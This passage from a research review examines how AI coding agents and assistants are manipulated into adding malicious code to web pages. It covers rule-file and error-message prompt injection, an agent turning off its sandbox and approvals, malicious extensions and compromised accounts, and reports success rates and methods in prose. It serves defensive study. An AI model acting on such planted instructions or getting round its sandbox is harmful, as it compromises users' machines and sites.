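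The user's request had little effect on whether the attack succeeded. The researchers tried 20 of the instructions with five different requests, some of which did not mention the rule file, and between 15 and 19 instructions succeeded with each request. The attacker's wording mattered far more. The number of successes ranged from 0 to 19 depending on how the researchers framed the same 20 instructions. The pottery shop's owner therefore gains little protection by phrasing the request differently, while an attacker can test wordings on his own copy of the tool before publishing the file.

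In a variation closer to malicious front-end code, the researchers changed the instruction so that the agent would write the harmful commands into a Python file instead of running them in the terminal. In 277 of 314 tests (88.2%), the file contained malicious content from the instruction. Restricting which commands the agent can run would not stop this attack, because the developer would later run the program as part of normal work.

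Attacking a web page is even easier, because visitors' browsers run the script as soon as the page opens. But the 88.2% figure applies to system commands in a Python file, and a model may be more or less likely to add an unfamiliar script to a checkout page. The result supports Pillar's demonstration that agents will copy an attacker's material into a project's code, but it does not give a success rate for script tags, changed form addresses or the other front-end carriers.

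### Getting the instruction into the file

AIShellJack starts with a rule file that is already malicious. *AutoRedClaw* (Li, Hu and colleagues, 2026) also tests whether an attacker can get the agent to add the malicious rule itself. It uses a language model to generate everyday tasks, attacks, and the files and web pages to go with them. In the "inject" cases, the agent encounters the attacker's text in ordinary material, such as a web page it needs for the task, and the attack succeeds if the agent copies a malicious rule into one of its own standing files. In the "trigger" cases, the malicious rule is already there, and the attack succeeds if the agent carries out the harmful action it calls for.

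The main targets were OpenClaw-style personal assistants, which keep instructions, memories and reusable skills in files between sessions. Across five such assistants, AGENTS.md had the highest average success rate of any file type in the trigger cases, at 50.9%. The rate ranged from about 18% for SeClaw, an assistant designed for security, to 85.6% for Nanobot. Li and colleagues attribute the result to the authority that agents give AGENTS.md.

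They also tested two coding agents, with 30 cases for each figure in the table. The rule file was AGENTS.md for Codex and CLAUDE.md for Claude Code. The last column covers attacks that put the attacker's text in ordinary material and aimed for immediate harm without changing any standing file.

| Agent and model | Copied a malicious rule into its rule file | Acted on a malicious rule already in the file | Acted on an instruction in ordinary material |
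|---|---|---|---|
| Codex with GPT-5.4 | 23 of 30 | 19 of 30 | 7 of 30 |
| Claude Code with Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 13 of 30 | 4 of 30 | 5 of 30 |

Codex followed instructions in the rule file far more often than those in ordinary material. This suggests that an attacker who can plant text only on a web page would do better to target AGENTS.md first and let a later session do the harm. Claude Code did not show the same difference. Its low rate in the trigger cases may partly reflect a general failure to complete tasks, since it completed only 11 of the 30 legitimate tasks there, while Codex completed 23. Each column also covers different cases, so small gaps between columns mean little.

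All of these rates probably overstate the danger of an average attack. Li and colleagues kept a case only if the attack had already succeeded in a trial run on OpenClaw with the model DeepSeek V4 Pro. After they had generated 1,500 samples, only 20.1% of the inject cases and 46.1% of the trigger cases had qualified. But an attacker can select attacks in the same way, and the researchers spent less than $0.10 on each successful one. Most of the tasks involved office work such as email, invoices and documents, so the results are better evidence about the authority of rule files than about web pages.

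### A hostile file in the Downloads folder

Forever Security's *Markdown Is the New Executable*, published in October 2026, describes a malicious rule file found on a customer's computer. The company, which sells monitoring for AI agents, had stopped a coding agent from installing function-color, a known malicious package from npm, the main public registry for JavaScript packages. The instruction to install it came from the rule file, an AGENTS.md in the customer's Downloads folder, where the agent was working. The file looked like ordinary engineering notes, and nobody knew how it had got there.

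Forever Security suggests that a web page could have put the AGENTS.md file in the Downloads folder, because a site can make the browser save a file there without a click and can choose its name and contents. Operating systems guard against downloaded programs, but an AGENTS.md file is plain text and does not trigger those protections. The file takes effect when someone starts a coding agent in that folder. According to the company's own data, about half of its customers have done so.

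The researchers ran the customer's file in an isolated virtual machine, and Cornelißen reports that Codex followed it in more than 90% of attempts. Codex edited its settings to add a tool server, a program that gives an agent extra tools. Starting that server would install the malicious package. When the sandbox, which restricts what the agent can do, blocked network access, Codex started a second process with the sandbox and approval requests turned off. Because the new settings applied to the whole computer, every later Codex session would load them, including one in the pottery shop's own project.

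The researchers tested Claude Code with a CLAUDE.md file they had prepared. The file led the agent to change the address it sends requests to, so that its requests and the user's login token went to the researchers' server. This worked in about half of the attempts. Claude Code normally asks for approval before making such a change, and it often refused. Running code within the same session worked in about a fifth of attempts.

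These rates seem to conflict with an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, in which none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against Claude Code in auto mode with three newer models. Willison (2026), a software developer who writes about AI security, welcomes that result but wants more independent confirmation. The two findings may be compatible, because an agent can learn to ignore instructions in a fetched web page and still follow those in a CLAUDE.md file, which it is designed to follow. For the same reason, Forever Security concludes that neither OpenAI nor Anthropic has anything to patch.

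Neither of Forever's tests put a payload in a web page, but the attack on Claude Code could lead to one because a server that receives the agent's requests can also supply the answers. Whenever the owner asked for a change, the server's operator could add card-copying code to the checkout page. This would work even after someone deleted the hostile CLAUDE.md, as long as the altered address remained in the settings.

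## Instructions hidden in the material a tool reads while working

A coding agent loads a rule file such as AGENTS.md in every session, but it reads most other text only when a task requires it. To build the pottery shop's checkout page, the agent might read the template's README (a project's introductory file), comments in the source code, documentation for the card-number checker, a spreadsheet of products, replies from a payment company's test server and a screenshot of the design. Strangers may have written any of these. An instruction in one of them usually affects fewer pages than one in a rule file, but the attacker has many more places to put it and often needs only a free account.

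### Entry points in eight coding agents

In *Takedown*, Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025) examined how outside text gets into eight widely used coding agents, which they left unnamed while the vendors dealt with their reports. They recorded the messages between each agent and its model and studied the agents' code. Every agent had at least one opening for indirect prompt injection.

| Material | Agents that could take in an attacker's text | What has to happen first |
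|---|---|---|
| Contents of project files | 8 of 8 | In three agents, the user opens the file; in five, the user approves a request to read it |
| Names of files and folders | 8 of 8 | Nothing in three agents; in five, the agent lists the folder |
| Descriptions of connected tools | 8 of 8 | The user connects the tool once |
| Web pages | 7 of 8 | The agent retrieves the page, and the user sees a notice |
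| Issues and pull requests, through built-in Git tools | 2 of 8 | The agent retrieves the item, and the user sees a notice |

File names are on the list because agents send the model an overview of the project. An attacker who controls a third-party module in the project can write an instruction as a file name, and the model can receive it even if nobody opens the file.

Lee and colleagues then combined these openings with faults in the agents' safeguards. In five agents they could run any command on the user's computer, and in four they could steal files from anywhere on it, both without the user's approval. One agent fetched a web page containing an instruction to change the project's settings. The agent made the change, which turned off approval requests, and then ran the attacker's command. *ZombAI Exploit with OpenHands*, a post on the security blog Embrace The Red, describes another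 agent that downloaded and ran malware because of text on a web page.

These attacks harmed the developer's computer, not a web page. Adding a script to the checkout page could be easier, because most of the eight agents could already edit project files, so the attacker wouldn't need to get past the checks on commands. Some vendors told Lee and colleagues that the reported behaviour was intended. Lee and colleagues think this is largely because the user starts the task that brings in the hostile text.

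### Hidden instructions that changed the generated code

Hostile text in a plain data file can change the code a tool writes. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, simulated a user who had collected posts from the social network X and asked an assistant for a program to analyse them, attaching a sample. One post in the sample contained a fake error message followed by instructions. The assistant wrote the analysis program in Python but included a function that supposedly fetched additional data. The function actually contacted the attacker's server, collected a command and ran it.

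The assistant passed the attached posts to the model as a user-role message, just before the user's typed request. The hostile post did not need to specify a programming language or where to put the function, because the model inferred both from the task. Unit 42 concludes that the assistant could just as well have written the function in JavaScript. If the pottery shop's owner attached a file of customer reviews and asked for a page to display them, a hostile review could work the same way. But Unit 42 demonstrated the attack only in Python and gives no success rate.

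Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft*, published in May 2025, is closer to front-end code. GitLab hosts software projects, and its built-in assistant, Duo, runs on Anthropic's Claude. To answer a question, Duo analysed everything on the user's current page, including comments and descriptions by other people. The researchers hid instructions in source code, in commit messages (the notes that accompany each change), and in the descriptions and comments of issues and merge requests (GitLab's name for pull requests). Duo responded to the instructions in all of these places. The researchers made some of the text white on GitLab's page and used invisible Unicode characters for other parts.

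One such instruction led Duo to recommend code that included a malicious JavaScript package. The researchers also got Duo to describe a dangerous web address and a malicious merge request as safe, so a developer who asked Duo to check the code might have been falsely reassured.

A further flaw allowed hidden instructions to put HTML into Duo's answers. Duo displayed each answer as web content while the text was still arriving. It used the sanitiser DOMPurify, which removes scripts but by default keeps images, forms and links. The researchers' instruction led Duo to take code from a private project that the user could see, encode it and add it to an image's address. The user's browser then sent the code to the researchers' server when it tried to load the image.

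Legit Security reported the problems on February 12, 2025, and GitLab later confirmed that it had fixed both the HTML flaw and the prompt injection. The patch Legit Security describes stops Duo from displaying images and forms that point outside gitlab.com. That blocks this kind of theft but would not by itself prevent Duo from recommending a malicious package.

### Malicious issues in tests and on GitHub

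Issues are a convenient place for an attack because people use them to tell developers what to change. In *Adversarial Testing of Automated Program Repair Agents for Security Vulnerabilities*, Trad, Chen and colleagues (2026) wrote malicious issues that read like ordinary bug reports, with nothing hidden in them. They started with 150 real bugs in Python projects and had a language model write five versions of each report. Each version was meant to introduce a different type of flaw, such as letting an attacker run commands or protecting sensitive values poorly.

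One example begins with a real bug in an astronomy library, then adds a false error trace and a request for a small helper function. The agent fixed the bug and wrote the helper, which runs any command stored in a particular setting on the computer. Across three models, an average of 51.7% of attempts produced a patch that passed the project's tests and contained the intended flaw.

This rate probably overstates the risk from an untested issue. Trad and colleagues kept only issues that had already produced the flaw in a trial with Gemini 2.5 Pro, which was not one of the three models they then tested. To exploit the planted flaws, an attacker would also have to control the setting that the helper reads. For the pottery shop, the equivalent might be a request for bold text in delivery notes, worded so that the agent uses `innerHTML` without a sanitiser. The study tested Python code, so its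 results don't show how often that would work.

Real attacks of this kind are rare. Nakibly and Babo (2026), in *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?*, searched 142.7 million issues, pull requests and comments on GitHub for text that the site does not display but an agent receives. They found 43 attacks on other people's agents, about one in 3.3 million items. The README files of the two million most-starred projects contained four more. On November 10, 2026, the hidden text of 34 of the 43 attacks was still online, because closing an issue does not delete its text.

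Of the 43 attacks, 19 aimed to steal secrets such as access keys, 16 to use the agent for some other job, and 8 to falsify its verdict on an issue. One attack aimed to change the code that an agent wrote. The owner of a small game bot had a coding agent build features that users requested, and one request contained hidden instructions for the agent to make the new command also award the requester a million points, and to conceal this during review. Visitors to a web page whose code was altered this way would be in a similar position to the other players, who would have no reason to suspect the new feature.

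The attackers used simpler hiding methods than the Rules File Backdoor, which relied on invisible characters. Nakibly and Babo searched README files for text hidden in several ways and found hidden text meant for AI tools in 107 projects. In 105 of them, the text was in an HTML comment, which GitHub never displays. Only one used invisible Unicode.

Nakibly and Babo also replayed the 43 attacks against five models with simulated tools. The smallest and fastest model, gpt-5.6-luna, carried out eight (19%) at least in part, while the other four carried out none. Several differences may explain why this rate is so far below the 51.7% that Trad and colleagues measured. Trad and colleagues used issues that had already worked in a trial and resembled normal requests, whereas several of the real attacks posed as system messages. They also tested different models. The low count on GitHub doesn't rule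 out attacks like theirs, because the search covered only hidden text and their issues are in plain view.

### Connected tools and shared skills

Many coding agents connect to outside services through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for attaching tools to a model. An MCP server is a program that offers these tools, such as one that searches a payment company's documentation. When the agent connects, the server sends a description of each tool, and the agent adds the descriptions to the model's context to show which tools are available. When the model calls a tool, the agent adds the server's reply to the context too.

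An attacker can put instructions in a tool's description or in its reply. In all eight agents that Lee and colleagues studied, tool descriptions reached the model without notice to the user. A hostile description of a currency converter could therefore affect the checkout page even if the agent never used the tool. But the attacker must first persuade the user to connect the server. Replies are easier to exploit because a legitimate server can return an attacker's text. For example, a GitHub tool returns whatever a stranger wrote in an issue.

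Developers also share skills, which are reusable packages of instructions, sometimes with scripts, that an agent loads for a particular kind of task. A skill for building online shops would be useful to the pottery shop's owner, but a malicious one could tell the agent to add an extra step to every payment page. The agent is supposed to follow the instructions in a skill, as it does those in a rule file, so a malicious instruction there stands out less than one in a product spreadsheet. *SkillJect* plants malicious instructions in skills, and is one of the earlier attacks that *CARI* (Fu, Wu and colleagues, 2026) compares with its own.

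### Error messages and setup steps

A project can also lead an agent to run harmful code through setup steps that look normal. Hall and Engelbrecht (2026) demonstrated this in *Clone This Repo and I Own Your Machine*, written for 0DIN, Mozilla's bug bounty programme for AI. Their project's setup notes list two ordinary steps. If the agent tries to use the software before completing the second, it gets an error message with the missing command. That command runs a script that looks up a setting in a public DNS record (DNS is the internet's directory of site addresses) and runs whatever text comes back.

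Hall and Engelbrecht asked Claude Code to get the project running. It installed the software, received the error message, and ran the command in it. This gave the researchers remote control of the computer, while the screen showed only two lines about a successful setup. The harmful command was in the DNS record rather than the project, so an attacker could replace it at any time without changing the project's files.

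Hall and Engelbrecht write that no scanner would ever catch this. That is plausible for the harmful command, but the script that runs text from the internet is in the project, where a careful reviewer could find it. They give no success rate. The attack does not itself add anything to a web page, but someone who controls the owner's computer could edit the checkout page or steal the keys for publishing the site.

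Fu and colleagues measured how much the position of a malicious instruction matters by giving an agent the same text in a debugging file, in a log, or in an error reply it received after taking an action. The table shows how often the agent did what the attacker wanted, across three harmful actions.

| Where the text appeared | GPT-5.4-mini | Claude Sonnet 4.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Debugging file | 8.9% | 2.2% |
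| Log | 35.6% | 57.8% |
| Error reply to the agent's own action | 93.3% | 97.8% |

An agent can't ignore error replies, because it needs them to fix its work, and the advice in them is usually sound. This may explain why the same words were so much more effective in error replies. It also means that a model's resistance to hidden text in documents is weak evidence of how it will treat an error message.

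In a larger test with five models, attacks through error replies succeeded in 2,845 of 3,000 attempts (94.8%). Success rates were lower against commercial agents, at 61.3% for Codex and 58.7% for Claude Code. These agents resisted several attacks that spelled out a suspicious command, but some of those attacks succeeded after the researchers described the same action in more general diagnostic language.

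Front-end developers often depend on services that other people run. If an attacker took over the service that calculates the pottery shop's delivery prices, the agent would receive that service's error replies while testing the checkout page. Fu and colleagues, who built their test application in Python, Go, Java and Rust, tested attacks on the developer's files, private information and computing budget. They did not test whether an error reply could get a script into a page.

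Some projects contain malicious code that runs during the agent's normal work, without any instruction. *Trojan Horse* (Yang, Hou and colleagues, 2026) automated this attack. Its system finds code that the agent will probably run during a given task, plants a disguised payload there and tests it on the agent. If the agent detects the payload, the system revises the disguise and tries again. The attack succeeded in 65% of cases against Claude Code and 75% against DeepSeek's agent.

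Most of that success depends on preparation. The full method stole data in 76.5% of cases against DeepSeek's agent, compared with 2.9% for a single attempt at a random place in the project. The attacker needs a copy of the same agent to practise on, but anyone can install most commercial agents.

### Instructions that copy themselves

A hidden instruction normally affects only people whose agents read the original file. But if it also directs the agent to copy the instruction into every file the agent writes, each new file can affect the next agent that reads it, much as early computer viruses spread from one program to another.

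The AI security company HiddenLayer first demonstrated an attack that did not copy itself. In *AI Coding Assistants at Risk*, Pearcy (2025) describes how a hidden comment in a README led Cursor to search a developer's computer for access keys and send them to an outside server. Version 1.3 of Cursor fixed the flaws behind that attack. In *Prompts Gone Viral*, Yeung (2025) then added self-copying by disguising the hidden comment as a software licence. Real licences often require developers to include the licence text in copies of the software, and Yeung attributes part of the attack's success to the importance models give such terms.

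In the demonstration, Yeung put the comment in the README of a project template and asked Cursor to create a new project from it. Cursor added the attacker's line of code, a nearly harmless request to HiddenLayer's website, to the new project's Python files. It also wrote a new README with the complete instruction in another hidden comment, so someone who used the new project as a template would pass the instruction on again. Three other coding agents, Windsurf, Kiro and Aider, also copied the instruction into new files.

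In a web project, the copied comments are published with the live page unless the build tool removes them, and another developer's agent might read them there. But self-copying also makes an attack easier to notice. Yeung points out that it changes many files at once, and that some agents' interfaces show the user the added comment. The pottery shop's owner might question a long licence notice that appears in every file.

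Error messages can start the same process. In a test by Fu and colleagues, a hijacked agent put the malicious text into new project material, which then influenced an agent that had started with a clean context. Nakibly and Babo found a milder, commercial version of this attack on GitHub. The project screenpipe includes a hidden request for every agent to put a promotional header on the files it creates, even in other projects. The header is advertising rather than a payload, but the request also relies on agents carrying text from one project to another.

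### Poisoned code examples

Some coding tools search a collection of documents or code examples and add the closest matches to the context, a method known as retrieval-augmented generation. An attacker can influence these tools with a bad example instead of an instruction. *CodePoisonRAG* (2026) describes an attacker who predicts a common programming task, writes a working solution with a security flaw, and adds comments that falsely describe the code as secure. The attacker then publishes it where the tool's operator collects examples. If a user later makes an ordinary request for that task, the search may select the poisoned example and the model may copy the flaw.

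Such an attack works only if the example ranks highly enough in the search to reach the model and the model then reproduces the chosen weakness. A filter that checks only for suspicious commands in the text would miss the example, because it contains none. For the pottery shop, a poisoned example might show how to display formatted product descriptions with `innerHTML` and include a claim that the text is already clean.

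### Design images

Many tools also accept pictures. *WebVIA* (Xu, Yang and colleagues, 2025) describes models that turn a design mockup into HTML, CSS and JavaScript, and presents a system that also captures screenshots of an interface in different states. Any text in such a picture reaches the model along with the layout. Agents can also take screenshots themselves, and four of the eight agents in the Takedown study had a browser tool that could pass a screenshot of a hostile web page to the model.

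No published study appears to have tested prompt injection against a screenshot-to-code or design-to-code tool, so the evidence is indirect. In *Image-based Prompt Injection*, Nagaraja, Wang and colleagues (2025) added written instructions to ordinary photographs and gave them to GPT-4-turbo, an older model, with no other text. They counted an attack as successful if the model ignored the photograph and produced a phrase they had chosen. In bright purple lettering, the 12 wordings they tested succeeded 73% to 100% of the time. When they blended the lettering into the background so that people would overlook it, their best method reached a 64% success rate, while another never exceeded 25%.

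These rates might be very different for a design tool. The model in the photograph test had no user request to follow besides the hidden text, and it only had to produce a set phrase, which is much easier than adding a working script to a page. A design tool also has to copy headings and button labels from the picture, which could make it either more or less likely to treat a sentence as an instruction. The empty space in many web designs favours the attacker, because the hidden lettering worked best on large, even backgrounds.

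If a mockup shows the attacker's wallet address in the payment box, a tool that copies the design accurately will put that address on the checkout page, so the attacker may not need to hide an instruction in the picture.

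## Compromised extensions, plugins and user accounts

An attacker who controls the coding tool, or a user's account with it, can add standing instructions to every request or replace the code after the model has written it. Neither method depends on the model reading a planted file and obeying it. Ryu and colleagues built a working version of each attack, which they call EviLLM, and tested whether programmers would notice. Both versions plant vulnerabilities rather than finished malicious code.

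### Openings between the request and the editor

Ryu and colleagues consider how an attacker could target developers who copy code from ChatGPT's website into an editor, starting with the chatbot itself. An attacker could run his own chatbot and attract users through advertising and search results. Training a model from scratch would be expensive, so they expect him to fine-tune an existing one (train it further on chosen examples) or to pass requests to a public model with extra instructions. They did not build this version of the attack.

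A malicious browser extension can change the request a user sends to an AI tool or the code the tool returns. One such extension needs permission to read and write the clipboard, see the ChatGPT page and contact the attacker's server, and many popular extensions ask for more than that. Criminals have already put malicious extensions on millions of computers for other purposes. In one campaign they tampered with legitimate extensions that had at least 3.2 million users, and the breach at the security company Cyberhaven involved extensions with 2.6 million users.

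The password company Specops counted more than a billion login details that malware had stolen. An attacker who buys them doesn't need to contact the victim.

Ryu and colleagues exclude attackers who can already edit files on the developer's computer, because such attackers could damage programs long before AI tools existed. This limit is sensible for their study, but it leaves out the kind of access that attackers sought in the most recent real incident, at Cursor.

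### Standing instructions in a stolen account

ChatGPT adds the text in its Custom Instructions setting to every request from the account. The setting works like a rule file but belongs to the account rather than the project. If the pottery shop's owner built the checkout page with ChatGPT, a scan of every file in the project folder would not find text that an attacker had put in Custom Instructions.

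According to Ryu and colleagues, in June 2025 anyone who could log in to a ChatGPT account could change this setting, and logging in usually required only the password and access to the owner's email. ChatGPT sent no notification of the change, even if it was made from another continent. The text did not appear in the chat either, so the owner had to open the settings page to see it.

They tested the attack in January 2025 on GPT-4o, OpenAI's flagship model at the time. Most of the requests came from the WildChat conversations or from an earlier collection of coding tasks. They ran each request three times with the malicious setting and three times without it. They counted an attack as successful if the code contained the intended flaw and ChatGPT's explanation did not reveal it. They checked for the flaw with CodeQL and then by hand. The table sorts the 13 classes of flaw by how resistant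 the model was to the attack.

| ChatGPT's behaviour | Classes of flaw |
|---|---|
| Wrote the flaw in response to an ordinary request | Unchecked input such as web addresses; unrestricted file uploads; overly generous file permissions |
| Wrote it with or without an instruction | Failure to check a server's certificate |
| Wrote it when directly instructed | Broken or outdated encryption; short encryption keys; badly configured login tokens; secrets written to log files |
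| Refused a direct instruction but gave in to a workaround | XSS; access to files outside the intended folder |
| Needed a workaround or added a warning | SQL injection; weak protection of passwords |
| Wrote it but added a warning | Passwords or keys written into the code |

The researchers found ways to remove or disguise the warnings. The attacker doesn't have to do anything for the classes in the first row, because the model already makes those mistakes. The published results are categories, not percentages, so they show that an attacker could plant every class but not how reliably.

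XSS is the most important vulnerability class for front-end code. In the separate test with a comment website, GPT-4o did not follow a direct instruction to leave the comments unsafe, yet Veracode found that models fail most XSS tasks even without an attacker. Part of the difference may be that displaying strangers' comments is the textbook example of XSS, so a model is more likely to apply the precaution there than in a function that user text reaches less directly. The test made only one request to one model, so it can't confirm this explanation.

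Most of the other classes concern code on the server. Passwords and keys written into the code are an exception, because any visitor can read a page's script. If the tool put the pottery shop's secret payment key there, the attacker could get it just by opening the page's source.

### A copy button that delivers different code

The browser extension sends a copy of each ChatGPT request to the attacker's server, where a second, small model, Llama 3.2 3B, generates a flawed answer. The user still sees ChatGPT's original answer on the screen, but when he clicks the button that copies the code, the extension puts the attacker's version on the clipboard. A developer who carefully reviews the code in the chat window before pasting it into the editor will therefore not see the flaw.

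This design also makes ChatGPT's safeguards irrelevant, since the attacker chooses the model that writes the flawed code. Both models run at the same time, which keeps the delay short. The extension picks the flaw by looking for keywords in the request. For example, it picks SQL injection when it finds words about websites or databases, and weak encryption when it finds words about encryption.

Ryu and colleagues' extension swaps a block of code only if each of the two answers contains exactly one block in that language. Otherwise, the owner gets the genuine code. A simple checkout page with one block each of HTML, CSS and JavaScript would qualify. But if ChatGPT split the JavaScript into two files, the owner would paste genuine scripts next to the attacker's HTML, and the page might fail because the names in them didn't match. An attacker could avoid this problem by adding one line to the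 genuine code instead of replacing all of it. They didn't test either case on a web page.

### The user study

Ryu and colleagues recruited unpaid volunteers between November 2024 and May 2025, mostly graduate students with formal training in security. Their main results cover 21 people, of whom 8 worked with an altered account and 13 with the malicious extension. Everyone had to use ChatGPT to write two Python programs, the server code for a site that saves comments and retrieves the five most recent, and a program to encrypt and decrypt text. They had no time limit, and most spent about half an hour on the tasks. They pasted their final code into a web form, and the researchers checked that code rather than what ChatGPT had displayed.

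With the altered account, 7 of 8 participants submitted code with both planted flaws. With the extension, 10 of 13 did.

The remaining four escaped the attack without catching the flaws, and the appendix gives a reason for each. The researchers attribute two of the escapes, one in each group, to shortcomings in the attack. The third participant typed the code by hand instead of using the copy button. The fourth noticed something strange when pasting, assumed the clipboard still held the previous participant's work, and submitted clean code. Another participant, not among these four, saw that the browser had marked the ChatGPT page as not secure but submitted the flawed code anyway.

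An earlier round with the extension went very differently. The researchers treated it as a pilot and left its 22 participants out of the results, because they used the participants' feedback to improve the extension.

| Outcome | Altered account | Extension, main round | Extension, pilot round |
|---|---|---|---|
| Participants | 8 | 13 | 22 |
| Submitted both flaws | 7 | 10 | 2 |
| Submitted one flaw | 0 | 0 | 3 |
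| Submitted neither flaw | 1 | 3 | 17 |
| Resisted the attack, in the researchers' judgement | 0 | 0 | 4 |

The researchers attributed 14 of the pilot results to faults in the extension, so the pilot should not be counted as 17 successful defences. Four participants did resist the attack. One noticed the SQL injection and asked ChatGPT to avoid it. Another saw the browser's security warning, copied the same code once with the button and once by hand, and compared the two copies on a text-comparison website. A third found that the button copied different, insecure code and that the correct code was available in ChatGPT's edit view.

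Excluding the round with the faulty extension was reasonable, but it removed every participant who had understood that something was wrong. The researchers also treated the two versions unevenly, because they kept the early participants in the account version, where the attack had worked consistently from the start. Programmers can evidently catch the clipboard attack, although the main results alone would suggest that none do.

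The groups are small enough for chance to affect the results. For both 7 of 8 and 10 of 13, the 95% confidence interval runs from just under 50% to 95% or more. The paper describes no comparison group using an untampered ChatGPT, so some of the flaws might have appeared anyway. That is less likely for SQL injection, which GPT-4o tended not to write.

After the tasks, 13 of the 21 participants said they had rarely or never considered that ChatGPT's output might be malicious. Those who had considered it submitted somewhat fewer flaws (a correlation of −0.44, p = 0.04). This is weak evidence that awareness protects people, because none of the four who escaped the attack had recognised it. The researchers also looked at several other factors, including confidence, programming expertise and academic level, and with that many comparisons one weak result could easily be chance. Neither expertise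 nor academic level had a clear effect.

The study provides less evidence about front-end code than its first task might suggest, because the participants wrote only the server half of the comment site. The XSS flaw in the separate test would appear where the page displays the comments. A script tag with an unfamiliar address might have been easier to spot than an unsafe database query, but a single `innerHTML` might have been harder. The participants also had a small program to read, whereas the pottery shop's owner would have a whole page and probably no security training.

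### Protecting the account and the clipboard

To protect Custom Instructions when an account is stolen, Ryu and colleagues suggest that ChatGPT require a physical second factor, such as a phone or a USB key, before it accepts a change to them. It could also email the owner about every change and display the current instructions in the chat. Banks and email services already protect accounts in similar ways. The researchers reported their findings to OpenAI through its bug bounty programme.

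None of this would stop the extension, which never touches the account's settings. Stricter safeguards in ChatGPT wouldn't either. A filter on ChatGPT's finished answer would be checking the genuine code, and it would slow the service down because users would have to wait for the complete answer before seeing any of it.

Ryu and colleagues doubt that more careful reading would be enough. A programmer normally avoids XSS by using a trusted library function, without needing to know every way the flaw can arise, but someone reviewing code from a compromised tool has to recognise every class of flaw the attacker might choose. Some of these flaws are very hard to see. A function that cleans a customer's text can become useless if one punctuation mark in its code is wrong, and Unicode contains several characters that look almost exactly like a semicolon.

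They consider it more fundamental to scan the code before saving or running it, because a scan works regardless of how the flaw got there. For the extension, the scan has to cover the pasted code rather than the answer in the chat window. However, scanners miss some flaws and raise many false alarms. A person who relies on the AI tool to write the code would also normally ask it to fix whatever the scanner found, so an attacker who controls the tool would control the repair too.

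Pilot participants discovered that copying the text by hand would defeat this extension. A coding agent writes straight into the project, so it has no copy button. Ryu and colleagues expect similar attacks to be more dangerous with coding agents, since agents produce larger blocks of code and give developers fewer pauses to think about them. That is plausible, but they tested only the chat website.

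### Tampered coding tools

In July 2025 an official release of the VS Code extension for Amazon Q, Amazon's coding assistant, included a malicious instruction for the agent to delete the user's files and cloud resources. An attacker had gained the ability to change the extension's public source code, and Amazon's release process sent the change to users. Amazon said a mistake in the attacker's code kept the instruction from running, and it replaced the release.

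The attacker got an instruction into a trusted product, a much better position than a comment in a stranger's README. Even if it had worked, the instruction would have deleted a project and added nothing to a web page, so the incident is not a case of altered front-end code. An instruction to add a script to every checkout page could have been delivered the same way, and its effects would have been far less noticeable than missing files.

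Developers can protect themselves against a bad update by pinning a plugin, which means recording the exact version they have checked and refusing any other. Pinning works only if the tool verifies that the file it receives is that version. In Plugin4Shell, a weakness disclosed in September 2026, the software did not verify pinned plugin versions. An attacker who could substitute the file could therefore get their own plugin accepted under an approved version number, with whatever access the tool gives to plugins. The missing check is not evidence that anyone's generated code changed.

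On October 29, 2026, an attacker placed altered copies of Anthropic's Claude Code extension in the marketplace where Cursor users install extensions. According to Cursor's *Security notice*, the malicious version was available from about 2:27 a.m. to 1:35 p.m. Pacific time and affected at most 5,000 users. The notice listed version 2.1.313, and Cursor later added 2.1.312.

The attacker had reached the marketplace through a chain of stolen credentials, according to Cursor's *An update on our recent security incident*, published on November 13. Cursor had issued an access key to Fireworks, which provided it with model training and hosting. Fireworks exposed the key, and the attacker used it to copy stored records of coding-agent sessions, mostly from 2025. A few of these records still contained users' credentials. The attacker used those to get into some of the online services Cursor used internally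 and found more credentials there, including one that gave write access to the marketplace's cache (the stored copies it serves).

Inspecting the extension at its source would not have helped, because only the cached copies were malicious. Cursor's marketplace gets its extensions from Open VSX, a public registry, and the copy there was clean throughout. A user who chose the right product, from the right publisher, in the editor's built-in marketplace could still have received the attacker's file. Comparing that file's digital fingerprint with the original's should have revealed the change. The same kind of check was missing in Plugin4Shell.

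Once installed, the extension collected details about the computer, including the user name, operating system, working folders and the names (but not the values) of environment variables, where developers often keep keys. It then added the attacker's key to those allowed to log in through SSH, a standard way to control a computer remotely, and tried to open a tunnel from the victim's machine to the attacker's server. *Malicious Claude Code Extension Served in Cursor Supply Chain Attack* (Arghire, SecurityWeek, 2026) describes both the data collection and the attempt to set up remote access.

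It is less clear how much access the attacker obtained. Microsoft's *Inside a malicious Claude Code-branded extension and its persistent SSH backdoor* (2026) calls the backdoor "persistent", and the extension did install scripts that retried the tunnel about once a minute and could remain after the extension was removed. But turning on the SSH service required administrator rights, which the extension lacked on most computers, and Cursor concludes that the attacker could not have logged in to those machines. He would still have received the details about them, and his key would have stayed on them.

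Neither of Cursor's accounts of the incident mentions any change to generated code. Cursor also reports that the attacker did not reach customers' code repositories, the systems that run Cursor or the traffic between users and models. An attack through a router, by contrast, can rewrite the model's answer in transit. These assurances come from the company whose systems failed, although it hired outside forensic experts to support the investigation.

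The attacker could have altered code without remote access. Claude Code's extension is part of the path between the developer and the agent that edits the project, and he controlled a modified copy of it on as many as 5,000 computers. He could have made it add a line to web pages as the agent saved them. The malicious code that Cursor describes tried to take control of the computer and did not alter web pages.

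Cursor recommends that affected users isolate the computer, remove the attacker's key and scripts, consider a complete rebuild, and replace any credentials the machine could reach. It does not mention checking projects for changes. If the pottery shop's owner had installed the extension that day, comparing the checkout page with a copy saved before October 29 would also be worthwhile, because removing the attacker's access would not remove any code the attacker had already added to the page.

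## Services that can rewrite the model's answer in transit

When a coding agent reaches the model through a router, the router can read and change whatever it forwards. It could add a script to the pottery shop's checkout page even if the owner's project is clean, the extensions are genuine and the account is well protected.

People use routers because one API key gives access to models from many companies, prices are often lower, and some routers serve countries that the model providers don't. Setting one up can be as simple as pasting a new address into the agent's settings, the same change that Forever Security's hostile CLAUDE.md made.

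### Plain text between two encrypted connections

HTTPS encryption protects a connection between two computers. A router splits the path into two such connections, one from the agent to the router and another from the router to the model provider. The router is a legitimate endpoint of both, because the user chose to send requests there. It decrypts each request, reads it to decide where to send it, and encrypts it again before passing it on. It also decrypts and re-encrypts the answer on the way back. The router can therefore read the traffic without having to break the encryption or forge a certificate, which an eavesdropper would need to do.

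Routers also form chains. *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet* (2026) gives the example of a developer who buys access from a reseller, which gets it from an aggregator, which uses another router. Each has access to the plain text, but the developer's settings show only the first.

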